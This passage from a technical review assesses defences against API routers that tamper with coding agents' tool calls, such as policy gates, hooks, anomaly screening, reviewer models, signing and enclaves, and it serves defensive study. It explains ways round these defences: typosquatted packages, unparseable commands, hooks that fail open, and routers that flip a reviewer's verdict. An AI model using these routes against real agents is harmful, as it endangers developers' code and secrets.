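Manual approval needs no extra software, and it can stop a conspicuous command, such as a download unrelated to the task. But the developer has to read every command, and a long turn with 300 commands takes 50 minutes to review at ten seconds each. Many people switch the prompts off, as they had in 91% of the sessions on the decoy relays that Liu and colleagues ran. Some agents let a developer approve one kind of command for the rest of a session, and that approval also covers altered commands of the same kind.

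Manual approval has no measured success rate, so it can't be compared with the automatic controls. Crosley advises people never to run auto-approved sessions through a router they don't control. If approving every call is too slow, a team can let the agent read project files without approval and require it only for calls where a mistake would do the most damage, such as installing packages, running downloaded programs or writing outside the project.

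### Fixed rules in a policy gate

A policy gate is a local rule that blocks tool calls outside a list of permitted domains, packages or commands. The gate that Liu and colleagues tested blocks shell commands that download from unlisted domains or install unlisted packages. If `requests` is on the package list, the agent can install it, but the gate blocks a command to install the misspelled `reqeusts`.

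The gate also has to deny any call it can't parse. A shell command can take the address it will contact from a variable, a file or another program's output, so the address may not appear in the command itself. If the gate blocked only commands that contained an unlisted domain, a router could get past it by sending commands the gate can't read. Denying by default, or failing closed, prevents this. It also stops some legitimate scripts, which the developer then has to simplify or approve by hand.

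Crosley reports that Liu and colleagues tested their gate on 1,000 harmless commands, 500 rewritten commands and 500 commands with substituted packages, all generated by their own scripts. The gate blocked every altered command and ten of the harmless ones (1.0%). These ten fetched installers from mirror sites missing from the domain list, so adding the mirrors would have let them through.

The gate stopped no attacks in a second, simpler benchmark, where the attacker had planned for it. The attacker either put the harmful file on a permitted domain or used a harmless-looking command to run a script that was already on the machine. The gate checks where a file comes from but not what is in it. Liu and colleagues still call it "the strongest immediately deployable control", but recommend it as a coarse filter for obvious risks.

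A rule that permits the whole domain of a large code-hosting site also permits an attacker's files, because anyone can publish there. Permitting only the project's own release address is safer, and also requiring a checksum is safer still. A checksum is a value computed from a file's contents that changes if the file does. The developer should get it directly from the project rather than from the agent.

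Crosley also noticed that one section of the paper describes a gate that checks only domains, which would let dependency substitution through, while the gate in the results section also has a package list. Anyone building a gate needs both a domain list and a package list. A project's existing list of dependencies is a good starting point for the package list, as long as the agent can't edit the copy the gate uses.

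### How a gate can stop working unnoticed

Claude Code can run a policy gate as a hook, a program it starts at set points in a session. According to Anthropic's *Hooks reference*, a `PreToolUse` hook runs before a tool call and can block it. However, several kinds of failure let the call continue. The table combines the reference with passages Crosley quoted from it in October 2026.

| What happens to the hook | What happens to the tool call |
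|---|---|
| It returns a `deny` decision or exits with code 2 | Claude Code blocks it |
| It exits with code 0 and no output | The normal permission rules apply |
| It crashes with another error code | The normal permission rules apply |
| It runs out of time | The normal permission rules apply |
| It never starts, because its path in the settings is wrong | The normal permission rules apply |
| Its filter doesn't match the call | The normal permission rules apply |

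If a gate crashes on an unusual command under auto-approval, the normal permission rules let the call run. The gate therefore gives no protection in the sessions that depend on it most. Crosley writes in *Claude Code Hooks Explained* that a crashed hook leaves an error notice in the transcript, but the notice helps only if somebody reads it.

A hook can easily fail open, as an example script in Anthropic's reference shows. The script blocks `rm -rf`, a command that deletes whole folders, and uses a separate program, `jq`, to read the tool call. If `jq` is missing, the script has no command to examine, so it exits with code 0 and the call continues. Anthropic tells readers to install `jq` first, and the script is a teaching example rather than a security gate.

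A real gate should exit with code 0 only after it has read the whole call and matched every part against its lists. In all other cases, including its own errors, it should exit with code 2. It needs an internal time limit shorter than Claude Code's, so it can deny the call before Claude Code stops waiting. Newer versions of Claude Code have an `onFailure` setting that can make a failed hook block the call. Whichever method a team uses, it should crash the hook on purpose to see whether the call is blocked, then request a harmless file from an unlisted domain to confirm that the gate is running.

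The hook covers only the tools its filter matches. A filter for `Bash` alone leaves out the tools that create and edit files, and on Windows it also leaves out PowerShell, which Claude Code treats as a separate tool.

How well a hook protects an agent also depends on where the team stores it. Anthropic states that cloud sessions don't read the settings file on a developer's own computer, so a hook defined only there won't run in those sessions. An injected edit to the project's settings file could disable a hook defined in that file. Administrators can avoid this by defining the hook in centrally managed settings, where user and project settings can't turn it off.

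Claude Code also passes the reason for a denial back to the model, so the reason travels through the router. A message listing the permitted domains would show a malicious operator how to get past the gate. The message should therefore include only the fact that a policy blocked the call, and the details should go into a local log.

### Why an allowlist blocked all the attacks in one study and a third in another

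Fu and colleagues tested a very similar control and got a much lower result. Their allowlist extracts the domains from web addresses in commands and the package names from installation commands, and permits a call only if all of them are on the list. Across four ways of injecting the call, it stopped between 30.8% and 44.1% of injections.

The difference comes mainly from what the researchers injected. Luo and colleagues provide a third comparison by checking altered code with a policy written for Open Policy Agent (OPA), a general tool for enforcing rules.

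| Study | Altered calls in the test | Share blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Liu and colleagues | 500 rewritten commands and 500 package substitutions | 100% |
| Fu and colleagues | 277 shell commands, 74 new files and 49 file edits | 30.8% to 44.1% |
| Luo and colleagues | Code edits that weaken security | 0% |

The gate in the first study had rules for domains and packages, and all 1,000 altered commands broke one of them. The test therefore shows that the gate works as designed, but it doesn't show how well those two rules cover the other changes a router could make.

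In 123 of the 400 samples that Fu and colleagues injected, the tool call created or edited a file, so the allowlist had no command to inspect. It could therefore block at most 277 samples, or 69%. If all the blocked calls were shell commands, the allowlist stopped between 44% and 64% of the shell commands. The commands it missed presumably named no unlisted domain or package, since a command can do damage using only what is already on the machine.

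The allowlist stopped 529 of 1,200 injections when the router added a call to the genuine response and 369 when it generated a new response around the call. This difference is hard to explain, because an allowlist gives the same answer every time it checks the same command, and each method of injection drew on the same 400 samples. Fu and colleagues don't account for it, so the exact percentages deserve less weight than the general result that an allowlist missed more than half of a varied set of attacks.

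The two studies also measure mistaken blocks differently. Liu and colleagues report the share of harmless commands that the gate blocked, which was 1.0%. Fu and colleagues report the share of blocked calls that were harmless, which was 29.7% to 43.9%. Their allowlist blocked between 224 and 292 harmless calls over 1,200 runs, or about one for every four or five runs.

### Screening for unusual calls

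An allowlist needs someone to maintain it. Anomaly screening instead scores each call by how unusual it looks and flags those above a threshold. VPN Central's *AI router flaws let attackers inject malicious code and steal sensitive data* explains that the version Liu and colleagues tested learns from harmless behaviour. According to Crosley, it uses features such as risky patterns in shell commands and the entropy of the arguments, a measure of how random their text looks.

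The screen caught 89.0% of rewritten commands, 50.0% of substituted packages and 50.9% of calls injected under a trigger, at a threshold that also flagged 6.7% of harmless calls. Substituted packages are harder to spot because installing a package is normal and a misspelt name looks much like a real one. The 50.9% probably reflects which calls the researchers put in that group, since a trigger doesn't change how an altered call looks when it arrives.

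Allowing fewer false alarms makes the screen much weaker. When Liu and colleagues let it flag only 1% of harmless calls, it caught 43.5% of rewritten commands and almost none of the substituted packages.

Even the 89.0% is less useful than it appears, because altered calls are likely to be rare. Suppose an agent receives 10,000 calls and a router has rewritten 10 of them. The screen would flag about 9 of the altered calls (10 × 0.890 = 8.9). It would also flag about 669 of the 9,990 harmless ones (9,990 × 0.067 = 669.3). The share of alarms that point to a real attack is

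8.9 / (8.9 + 669.3) ≈ 1.3%

A developer would have to examine about 76 alarms to find one altered call. At 30 seconds each, the 678 alarms would take more than five and a half hours. The same calculation for the other results gives:

| Control | Altered calls caught, of 10 | Harmless calls flagged or blocked | Share of alarms that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| Screening at 6.7% false positives, rewritten commands | 8.9 | 669 | 1.3% |
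| Screening at 6.7% false positives, substituted packages | 5.0 | 669 | 0.7% |
| Screening at 1% false positives, rewritten commands | 4.4 | 100 | 4.2% |
| Policy gate, attacker who hasn't planned for it | 10 | 100 | 9.1% |

The rate of 10 in 10,000 is an assumption, since nobody has measured how often a malicious router rewrites calls. For half of the alarms to be real, about 7% of all calls would have to be altered. In the field studies, researchers detected no injections from most routers. With an honest router, all of the roughly 670 alarms would be false, and a developer who investigated them would soon start ignoring new ones.

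Liu and colleagues recommend using screening to decide which calls to review first. If a team already suspects a router and has time to read 50 calls, the 50 with the highest scores are a better choice than 50 picked at random. Automatically blocking calls based on their scores would interrupt ordinary work far too often.

Luo and colleagues tested other detectors on altered code, allowing each a false-positive rate of 5%. The best was a perplexity filter, which uses a language model to measure how unpredictable a piece of text is. It caught 30% of the altered APPS solutions and 9% of the altered Django patches. A classifier trained to recognise prompt injection caught 2% and 9%. Flagging 5% of calls at random would catch about 5% of the attacks, so the classifier did worse than chance on APPS. This is reasonable, since it was built to find hidden instructions and the altered code contained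 none.

### Review by a second model

Unlike a list of domains, a language model can assess what a command would do. Fu and colleagues gave a reviewing model a summary of the task, the most recent tool calls and the pending call, which it reviewed in two stages. The first stage strongly favoured blocking and allowed only a short answer. The second re-examined anything the first had flagged and could make exceptions, though overriding a block required the user's explicit confirmation.

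The table gives the range for each reviewer across the four ways of injecting a call:

| Reviewer | Injections blocked | Share of blocked calls that were harmless |
|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 39.8% to 64.4% | 21.1% to 25.9% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 39.1% to 62.1% | 9.0% to 14.3% |
| Kimi-2.7 Code | 40.3% to 49.9% | 41.0% to 53.2% |
| Qwen3.6-Plus | 50.8% to 64.0% | 14.9% to 20.4% |

Qwen was the most consistent at stopping injections, and DeepSeek-V4-Flash interfered least with harmless work. The two DeepSeek models and Qwen did best when the injected call replaced the whole response and came with no explanation. When the router generated a fitting response around the call, DeepSeek-V4-Pro's blocking rate fell from 64.4% to 39.8%. A convincing explanation may have helped the call get through, but it may not account for the whole drop, because the blocking rate of the allowlist, which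 ignores explanations, also fell, from 34.9% to 30.8%.

In these experiments, edits to existing files didn't trigger a review, and 49 of the 400 samples were edits. The allowlist doesn't inspect edits either, so about 12% of the injections would have passed both controls. Fu and colleagues didn't test the two controls together, but their separate results imply that the allowlist and the best reviewer combined would have stopped between 64% and 88% of the calls that replaced a whole response. A team using this kind of review should check that it covers file edits.

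A reviewer's blocks are also less reliable when attacks are rare. As the reviewer, DeepSeek-V4-Flash blocked 745 injected calls and 74 harmless ones over 1,200 runs that all contained an injection. If only one run in 100 had contained one, it would have blocked about 7 injected calls and still at least 74 harmless ones, so more than 90% of its blocks would have been mistakes.

Reviewers may block fewer harmless commands in other settings. *aegish*, a prototype Linux shell that has a language model classify each command, accepted between 96.8% and 100% of 496 harmless commands, depending on which of nine models it used. At 96.8%, it would still block about 320 of every 10,000 harmless commands.

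Fu and colleagues measured all their rates with reviewers that connected directly to the official service. The agents' built-in reviews, which went through the router, stopped none of the injections. A router that carries the review could replace the pending call with a harmless one before the reviewer reads it, or change the verdict from "block" to "allow" before it reaches the agent.

Developers who use a router because they can't reach the provider directly may find it hard to arrange a separate connection. The reviewer doesn't have to be the agent's model, so a smaller model on the developer's own computer would do, as would one from any provider they can reach directly. Sending reviews through a second router is riskier, because both routers could buy access from the same upstream supplier. Each reviewed call also needs an extra model request, which adds cost and delay, and an outside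 reviewer receives details of the project.

### Limiting what a command can reach

A sandbox restricts which files a command can read or change and which network addresses it can contact. *Agent Command Execution Safety* lists several Linux features that can enforce these limits, including network isolation and seccomp, which restricts the requests a program can make to the operating system. The limits apply whatever the command looks like, so a sandbox can contain an attack that every other control has missed.

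A router can obtain secrets from a sandbox even if the sandbox blocks all network access. The agent runs outside that restriction and sends each command's output through the router to the model as part of its next request. If an altered command prints a password file, the router receives the file's contents. Filtering the output for sensitive data can catch some of these leaks, but keeping real credentials and private files out of the sandbox is safer.

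A sandbox also can't contain harm that is built into the finished work. The weakened Django patch that Luo and colleagues produced would do no damage on the developer's machine, but it would become dangerous once the developer merged it and the website went live. Work from a sandbox therefore needs the same review as code from an unknown contributor.

The main drawback is inconvenience. Agents often need to download packages, reach an internal service or use a credential to deploy a program, and an injected command can use any access the developer grants for these tasks. A sandbox that the team rebuilds for each task limits how long a malicious package can remain installed. It also makes auto-approval much less dangerous, although the files the agent produces still need checking.

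### What a content check can't establish

Luo and colleagues argue that checks of this kind can't solve the underlying problem, because they examine what a tool call contains and not where it came from. Let *f*(*c*) be the result of any check on the content of a tool call *c*, and let auth<sub>S</sub>(*c*) equal 1 only if model *S* really produced it. Suppose the model requests a command in one session and a router injects the identical command in another. Then *f*(*c*) must be the same in both sessions, but auth<sub>S</sub>(*c*) is 1 in the first and 0 in the second, so no *f* can match auth<sub>S</sub> in both. Giving the check the rest of the conversation doesn't help if the injected call also fits the conversation.

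In many cases this wouldn't matter much. If a router injects a command to install the genuine `requests` package, the developer gets an extra package but little harm. It matters more for calls that are harmful in one place and normal in another. Django has a legitimate function for marking text as safe to display without escaping, and the router in Luo and colleagues' experiment used it on text that wasn't safe. Banning the function would block legitimate code, so a monitor would have to analyze that part of the program to tell safe uses from unsafe ones. Luo and colleagues accept that a monitor tuned for each project could catch some of these edits, but never with certainty.

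They also tested four defences designed for prompt injection, using Claude Opus 4.6 on the AgentDojo benchmark. Altered responses succeeded in 74.6% of cases without a defence and in 45.6% to 52.9% with one. The defences also reduced the share of users' tasks that the agent completed, from 87.2% to between 37.9% and 71.9%. CaMeL, which separates the agent's plan from untrusted data, had the lowest completion rate. It cut the attack's success rate to about 15% until the researchers adapted the attack to it.

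Local controls are practical because a developer can install them today without waiting for any provider or router to cooperate. They target the kinds of altered commands and packages that Liu and colleagues found in public routers. A gate with both lists would probably have stopped some of those calls, but the published block rates were measured on synthetic samples, not on the commands the nine routers sent. Router operators may also adapt if gates become common.

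Local controls would still be necessary even if providers signed tool calls. If prompt injection misleads the model into requesting a harmful download, the provider's signature on that request would be valid. A gate that blocks the domain stops the download whether the model or a router wrote the command.

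## Checking a provider's signature on a tool call

A local gate can block a download from an unknown domain, but it can't determine whether the model or a router wrote the command. It could if the provider signed each tool call before sending it. The provider would compute the signature from the call and a private key that nobody else holds, and anyone with the matching public key could check the signature. A router could still read a signed call, but any change would invalidate the signature, and the router couldn't produce a valid new one.

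### From the provider to the agent

For the earlier request to run `cat README.md`, response signing would work like this:

1. The model requests the command. The provider signs the parts of the response that the agent will execute and attaches the signature.
2. Each router reads what it needs for billing and routing, then forwards the response with its signature.
3. A small program on the developer's machine, which Luo and colleagues call a shim, receives the response before the agent does. It checks the signature with a public key it already holds.
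4. If the signature is valid, the shim passes the tool call to the agent. Otherwise it discards the call and reports an error, so the command never runs.

The agent needs no modification, because the developer only has to enter the shim's address where the router's used to be.

Liu et al. and Luo et al. both compare this with DKIM (DomainKeys Identified Mail), a standard for signing email. Email also passes through servers that can read and change it. Under DKIM, the sender's domain signs the message and publishes its public key, so the recipient can check the message without trusting the servers in between.

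### What the signature has to cover

Crosley reports that Liu and colleagues propose a signed envelope with five fields: the model identifier, the tool name, the arguments, the finish reason (why the model stopped) and a client nonce. The nonce is a random value that the client generates for one request and never reuses. The provider copies it into the signed response. If a router saved a signed command and delivered it in response to a later request, the client could detect the replay because the nonces wouldn't match.

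The client has to choose the nonce itself. If the provider chose it, the client wouldn't know which number to expect and so couldn't recognise an old response, as Flores (2026) points out in *The AIRP Provenance Seal and Serving Register*, a proposed internet standard for signed model responses.

Luo and colleagues designed and built a similar scheme, called sign-c. It covers slightly different fields:

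| Signed field | What a router could do without it | Liu and colleagues' envelope | sign-c |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool name | Send the arguments to a different tool | Yes | Yes |
| Arguments | Change a command, address or package | Yes | Yes |
| Finish reason | Make the agent stop or continue at the wrong point | Yes | Yes |
| Model identifier | Pass off one model's call as another's | Yes | No |
| Call identifier | Pair a result with the wrong call | Not listed | Yes |
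| Nonce, or session and turn | Deliver a signed call from an earlier exchange | Nonce | Session and turn |
| Fingerprint of the request | Deliver a signed answer to a different request | Not listed | Yes |

In sign-c, the provider's side signs a short record *b*:

*b* = ⟨*s*, *t*, *H*(κ(*q*)), *H*(κ(*c*))⟩

Here *s* is the session, *t* is the turn, *q* is the request and *c* is the part of the response that the agent executes. The function κ puts data into a standard form, and *H* is a hash function, which turns data of any length into a short fingerprint. The shim recomputes *b* from the request it sent and the tool call it received. It passes the call on only if the two records match and the signature is valid.

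Leaving out the model identifier weakens sign-c slightly. The shim accepts only responses signed with the key assigned to their route. But if a provider used one key to sign responses from all its models, a router could substitute a cheaper model from the same provider unless the fingerprint of the request covered the model's name.

### When the router changes the request

Suppose a developer asks the agent to fix a bug, and the router replaces that request with an instruction to install a certain package but leaves the nonce unchanged. The model follows the instruction, and the provider signs the resulting command. When the command reaches the developer's machine, the signature is valid, the nonce is correct, and nobody has changed the tool call since the model produced it. All five fields that Liu and colleagues list would pass the check.

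The router could send the victim's nonce with its own request, through its own account, so it doesn't need to deceive the model about who is asking. Few models would refuse a request to install an ordinary-looking package.

A signature that also covers the request prevents this. The provider would sign a fingerprint of the altered request, the shim would compute one from the original, and the two wouldn't match. Because an agent sends the whole conversation with each request, the fingerprint can also expose changes to earlier messages and tool outputs.

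sign-c signs in both directions. The shim signs each outgoing request with its own key, so the provider's side can reject an altered one before the model answers it. However, Luo and colleagues define κ by what it keeps from a response, which is the tool calls and the finish reason, and don't spell out what it keeps from a request. A session's first request contains no tool calls, so if κ kept only those fields, every first request would have the same fingerprint. To stop the attack, κ has to include the user's messages, the general instructions and the tool definitions.

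Their suggestion for a future standard is weaker than the system they built. They propose that providers add an `X-Model-Signature` header to each response, containing a signature over *H*(κ(*c*)) alone. That would prove that the provider's model once produced this tool call, but not who it was for, when it was produced or what it was answering. A router could collect signed commands from its own sessions and deliver them to anyone. A provider that adopts this should sign all of *b*.

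Binding the request causes mismatches even with honest routers, because many of them add instructions and tool definitions for ordinary reasons. Flores therefore has the client report a mismatch without rejecting the response. That may be reasonable for a chat, but an agent would then run a command that was generated for a request its user never made.

*AEX* (Guan, 2026), a design for signing requests and responses together, lets the client choose which fields of the request to bind. For instance, the client might leave out a tracking number that a company gateway adds. The client can also bind the absence of a field, so that the check would fail if the client sent no separate field for instructions and a router added one. A router can exploit any field left unbound, so the client should always bind the messages, instructions and tools.

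### Signing the meaning instead of the bytes

Honest routers also reformat responses. The first line below shows the arguments as the provider might send them, and the second shows how a router might deliver them:

```json
{"command":"cat README.md","workdir":"/code/project"}
{"workdir": "/code/project", "command": "cat README.md"}
```

Both lines have the same effect, but a signature over the exact characters of the first would fail on the second. Email signatures have the same problem. DuoCircle, an email security company, explains that DKIM has a "simple" form that accepts no modification and a "relaxed" form that tolerates changes such as extra spaces.

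The canonical form κ corresponds to the relaxed option. It extracts the identifier, name and arguments of each tool call, in order, along with the finish reason, and writes them in a fixed format. The two lines above therefore have the same fingerprint, but changing the file name changes the fingerprint. Luo and colleagues compared several choices of what to sign, using 439 pairs of original and altered responses. Signing the surrounding text as well caused honest traffic to be rejected whenever a router had reformatted that text, and signing the raw bytes failed as soon as a field was reordered. Signing less than the whole tool call let alterations through.

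Flores chose to have the signature cover a response's exact bytes so that two programs can't disagree about whether it is valid because they extracted different content from the same response. However, this rules out any router that reorders fields, even one that a company runs itself.

Converting between providers' formats is harder than normalising whitespace. *Tool-Use Binding* (2026) explains that Anthropic puts a call's arguments in a field named `input`, while OpenAI uses `function.arguments`. Anthropic's field holds a JSON object, and OpenAI's holds a string that contains JSON. A general-purpose rule for standardising JSON would leave the string's contents unchanged, so κ has to decode the string first. The two companies also name the same finish reason differently. If a router assigned its own call identifiers during the conversion, the signature check would fail even though the command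 was intact.

Streaming adds another complication, because the response arrives in pieces and the provider can't sign the whole of it until the model has finished. Guan links the pieces in a chain:

chain<sub>*i*</sub> = *H*(chain<sub>*i*−1</sub> ∥ *H*<sub>*i*</sub>)

*H*<sub>*i*</sub> is the fingerprint of piece *i* and its position, and ∥ means joining two values end to end. The chain starts from the fingerprint of the request. Removing, adding or reordering a piece changes every later value, and so does cutting the response short. But an honest router that merges two pieces also changes the chain. Guan proposes that routers the client trusts sign a receipt for each change they make. This allows honest changes, but the client has to trust those routers again.

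An agent also has to wait for the signature before it acts. Under Flores's rules, the client must refuse any content that arrives after the final signature. Otherwise a router could add an unsigned command at the end.

### Missing signatures and trusted keys

A router that can't forge a provider's signature can still delete it, and that would be enough for an attack if the shim accepted unsigned responses. sign-c prevents this by pinning each route. Before any traffic arrives, the shim stores the route's public key and a rule that the route always signs its responses. It then treats a missing signature as a failure. On a pinned route, the router can only withhold the response, which the developer would notice.

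The shim can't safely get the key from the router, since a dishonest router would supply its own. Luo and colleagues suggest that the shim fetch the key directly from the provider's website over TLS. If all traffic must go through the router, the shim's signed installation package can include the key. Neither method helps a customer who downloads the shim from the reseller that the shim is supposed to check.

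Flores uses the domain name system (DNS), the internet's directory of addresses, as email does. A provider would publish a record stating whether it signs every response, along with a fingerprint of its keys. The keys would be in a separate register that another organisation signs. To substitute false keys, an attacker would need both that organisation's signing key and control of the provider's domain. The register would normally expire after an hour, so clients would learn quickly that a provider had withdrawn a stolen key, whereas a key inside an installation package stays there until someone updates the package.

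Pinning also interferes with legitimate fallback from one provider to another. The shim would reject the second provider's answer unless it also held that provider's key. If the second provider doesn't sign its answers, the developer would have to accept unsigned answers or give up the fallback.

### The results for sign-c

Luo and colleagues tested sign-c on New API, the open-source router described earlier. No provider took part, so they ran their own signing program on the router to simulate one. They replayed the altered responses from their coding experiments, 353 from APPS and 58 from Django, and sign-c rejected all of them. It also stopped the Django edit in Claude Code before the agent applied it. On AgentDojo, with Claude Opus 4.6, it reduced the attack's success rate from 74.6% to zero.

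The 100% rejection rate is unsurprising, because a signature check will detect any change to a field the signature covers unless someone breaks the cryptography or the program has a bug. *Signed but Not Safe* (Chen, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) reports the same kind of result for its own signatures only as a sanity check.

It is more useful to ask whether signing interferes with honest traffic. Luo and colleagues found no false rejections in 694 AgentDojo responses, and none among the unaltered originals of the coding responses. By the calculation used for the sample of routers, the true rate in the AgentDojo test could still be as high as 0.43%, or about one rejection in a turn with 300 calls. But false rejections would probably come from particular kinds of reformatting rather than occur at random, so the kinds the test included matter more than the number of responses.

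The test included reordered fields and changed spacing on New API. Luo and colleagues acknowledge that it didn't include streamed responses that a router reassembles or conversion between providers' formats. Codex receives its responses as a stream, and converting formats is one of the main things routers do, so the zero result doesn't cover much of the traffic that sign-c would have to handle.

On AgentDojo, the agent completed 80.9% of users' tasks with sign-c in place, compared with 87.2% with no attack and no defence. Most of the difference came from tasks involving the chat service Slack, where completion fell from 95.2% to 76.2%. Luo and colleagues don't explain the drop, but it is much smaller than the drop under any of the four prompt injection defences they tested.

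Speed isn't an obstacle. The median cost of each call was:

| Step | Time |
|---|---|
| Signing the response | 1.960 ms |
| Checking the signature | 0.589 ms |
| Encrypting the request | 0.290 ms |
| Decrypting the response | 0.132 ms |
| Total | 2.971 ms |

The model took a median of 17,796 ms, so the 2.971 ms overhead was 0.0167% of the model's time. Signing and checking the request adds about 0.16 ms. If the model answered in one second, the overhead would be about 0.3%, and a turn with 300 calls would take roughly an extra second in total.

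### Secrets, text and bad decisions

A signature doesn't encrypt the conversation, so a router can still copy every password and file in it. According to Crosley, Liu and colleagues point out that secrets are already exposed on the way to the provider, before the provider has anything to sign. A separate, optional layer in sign-c encrypts the body of each message and leaves only routing information, such as the model's name, readable. This protects secrets from the router, but the provider's side must decrypt the messages.

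sign-c also leaves the model's text unsigned. If the response contains no tool call, a router could rewrite the final message to report that all tests had passed, or to ask the developer to paste a command into a terminal. Some agents execute code that they find in the text itself, and for them κ would have to cover that text too.

Most importantly, signing doesn't stop prompt injection, because the provider signs whatever a misled model requests. Chen and colleagues measured a similar problem in multi-agent systems, where one agent read a user's request, listed its requirements and passed the signed list to the others. Signing the list stopped every violation caused by changes in transit. But when the researchers added one adversarial line to the input before the agent wrote its list, unsafe decisions rose from 14.6% to 37.5% with Qwen3-8B, from 11.1% to 63.9% with gpt-oss-20b and from 16.7%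 to 97.2% with gemma-4-12b. In each of those decisions, the list was already wrong when the agent signed it. Signing has the same limit for coding agents, but the percentages don't carry over, because these were small models passing messages to each other without a router.

### Deployment by late 2026

There is no public evidence that any major provider had deployed signed tool calls by late 2026. In April, Liu and colleagues knew of no major provider that signed them. In August, Flores wrote that model responses carried no verifiable statement of what had produced them. When Crosley rewrote his commentary in October, he still described provider signatures as a future development, but he was relying on the April finding. A provider could have added signing since then, so readers can check its API documentation for a signature field and a published verification key.

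*AFiR SPICE Profile* (2026), a draft specification from a smaller project, reports that signed tool calls have been used in production since June. This is the project's own claim, and it doesn't show that OpenAI, Anthropic or any other major provider signs its responses.

The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to outside tools, also lacked such a mechanism when Liu and colleagues examined it. In *Attested Tool-Server Admission*, Metere (2026) writes that MCP standardises how messages travel "but not trust", and proposes an extension that controls which tool servers an agent may use. In *MCPS*, Sharif (2026) proposes signing each MCP message without changing the protocol. His March draft was set to expire on September 14.

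Even signed MCP messages wouldn't stop a router from rewriting tool calls. MCP carries a call from the agent to a tool server, after the model's response has passed through the router. If the router had changed the call, the agent would unknowingly sign the altered version.

The proposals for signing model responses are also at an early stage. Guan tested a prototype on simulated services. The IETF listed an earlier version of Flores's proposal, *The AIDP Provenance Seal and Serving Register*, as an individual submission, so no working group had adopted it. Providers, router developers and agent makers would have to agree on one canonical form, and the proposals differ on whether to have one.

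Incentives may be a bigger obstacle than the engineering. Luo and colleagues argue that a provider needs only one key pair and one signature per response, and that its users benefit even if no other provider signs. They also suggest that a user could adopt sign-c alone, but this seems wrong for anyone who buys from a reseller, because something has to sign the response before it reaches the first untrusted router, and the customer doesn't control that end of the path.

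A provider would have to manage keys and handle complaints when an honest router breaks a signature. Much of the benefit would go to people who reach its models through resellers, including some it may not want as customers. Signing also creates a risk for the provider because, as Flores notes, if it signs a response under the wrong model's name, the customer has lasting proof of the false claim. Resellers that quietly substitute cheaper models have an even stronger reason to resist signing.

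Companies with their own gateways are more likely to create demand for signatures, because they pay providers directly and can ask for signatures in a contract. OpenAI and Anthropic are also well placed to start, since each makes both a model and a coding agent and could sign the model's tool calls and have the agent check them. Luo and colleagues reported the problem and a proposed fix to Anthropic and other agent makers, but don't say how the agent makers responded. For developers who can't wait for providers, the one other way to protect tool calls in transit is to use a router that runs in protected hardware. Xie and colleagues designed one that needs no help from the provider.

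## Running the router in hardware the user can verify

AEGIS, which Xie and colleagues designed, removes the router operator's access to plain text. It moves the part of the router that handles messages into a protected area of the operator's computer, where the user can check which program is running. The provider doesn't have to change anything.

### Enclaves, measurements and attestation

A hardware enclave runs a program in isolation from everything else on the machine. The machine's owner can start and stop the enclave, but even the operating system can't read or change what is inside. AEGIS uses Nitro Enclaves, a service from Amazon Web Services (AWS).

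The user can't tell from isolation alone which program is inside the enclave, so the platform also computes a measurement, a hash of the exact software image that it loads. Any change to the program produces a different measurement. AWS's *Cryptographic attestation* describes separate measurements for the whole image, the kernel with its start-up code, and the application.

An attestation is a document, signed by the platform, that contains the enclave's measurements. If the operator starts the enclave in debug mode, the measurements are all zeros, and a careful client rejects them.

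A genuine document could still be a copy from another enclave or an earlier session. To prevent this, AEGIS has the enclave include in the document a nonce that the client chose and a fingerprint of the certificate for the current connection.

### One request through AEGIS

The developer points the agent at a sidecar, a small program on the developer's own machine. A request to read the README file then goes through these steps:

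1. The sidecar connects to the enclave, sends a nonce *n* and receives the attestation document.
2. It checks the platform's signature and compares three values in the document with what it expects: the measurement must equal *m*\*, the value the developer approved earlier, the nonce must equal *n*, and the fingerprint must equal *H*(certificate). If any check fails, the sidecar sends nothing.
3. The sidecar encrypts the conversation and the developer's router credential and sends them to the enclave.
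4. The enclave passes the credential and a few labels to the operator's ordinary software, which runs outside the enclave. That software replies with an account, the provider's key for it and the name of a destination.
5. The enclave looks up the name in a list of addresses inside the measured image. If the name isn't there, the request fails. Otherwise the enclave connects to the provider over TLS and forwards the conversation unchanged.
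6. The enclave forwards each piece of the response unchanged. It then reports the token counts, status and response time to the operator for billing.

The operator's machine carries all of this traffic, but only in encrypted form. It can specify a destination by name but not by address, so it can't send the text to a server the operator controls.

The encrypted connection protects each piece of the response as it arrives, so the agent can act on a tool call before the response ends. If a signature over the whole response were used instead, the agent would have to wait for the full response to verify it.

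### Why one change covers rewriting, triggers and copying

An operator has to read a tool call to rewrite it usefully, even if the rewrite only swaps a package name. If the operator alters the encrypted data blindly, the connection rejects it.

Triggers serve no purpose on this hardware. The operator can still count an account's requests, so a router could wait for the fifty-first, but it would have no readable tool call to change. Users can inspect the code that handles the text, so they no longer have to estimate how many test sessions would set off a hidden trigger.

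Copying requires the same access, so AEGIS also prevents the operator from getting the passwords and files in the conversation. The operator still receives the developer's router credential, but it issued that credential itself.

### What the evaluation tested

Xie and colleagues first ran four attacks against an ordinary router with access to plain text: rewriting a tool call, substituting a package, rewriting only under a trigger, and copying secrets. All four succeeded, and AEGIS blocked all four. The AEGIS result was largely to be expected, because the design leaves the operator no point at which to make the change.

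The tests of what the operator can still influence are more informative. The enclave rejected an unknown destination supplied by the host, and it didn't follow a server's attempt to redirect a request to an attacker's address. The researchers also captured the traffic on the operator's machine during a live response and found only ciphertext.

The AEGIS code that handles plain text has 851 lines in five files. By a broader count, AEGIS has 1,236 lines and the nearest comparable open gateway has 10,434, more than eight times as many.

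AEGIS carried three interfaces without converting between them: OpenAI's Responses, OpenRouter's Chat Completions and Google's Gemini. The researchers sent 100 synthetic requests through each, and all 300 succeeded. They didn't report a test of Anthropic's interface, so the results don't show that Claude Code would work through AEGIS unmodified.

The relay added little delay:

| Measurement | Median added time |
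|---|---|
| Small request, same relay code outside an enclave | 3.7 ms |
| Small request, AEGIS | 5.7 ms |
| 1 MB request, AEGIS | 52 ms |
| 4 MB request, AEGIS | 183 ms |

Opening a verified session takes another 12 ms, but only once. For small requests, a turn with 300 calls would take about 1.7 seconds longer (300 × 5.7 ms). But requests grow because an agent sends the whole conversation each time. If every request were 1 MB, the same turn would take about 16 seconds longer, though the delay would mostly still be small compared with the model's response time. The researchers measured these delays with a modified image and a local stand-in for the provider, so the figures exclude variation from the provider.

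### From a measurement to code that somebody has read

An operator could write a router that rewrites shell commands, run it in a genuine enclave and publish its measurement. The attestation would be valid, because it proves which code is running but not that the code is harmless. A user therefore has to connect the measurement to source code that somebody has reviewed:

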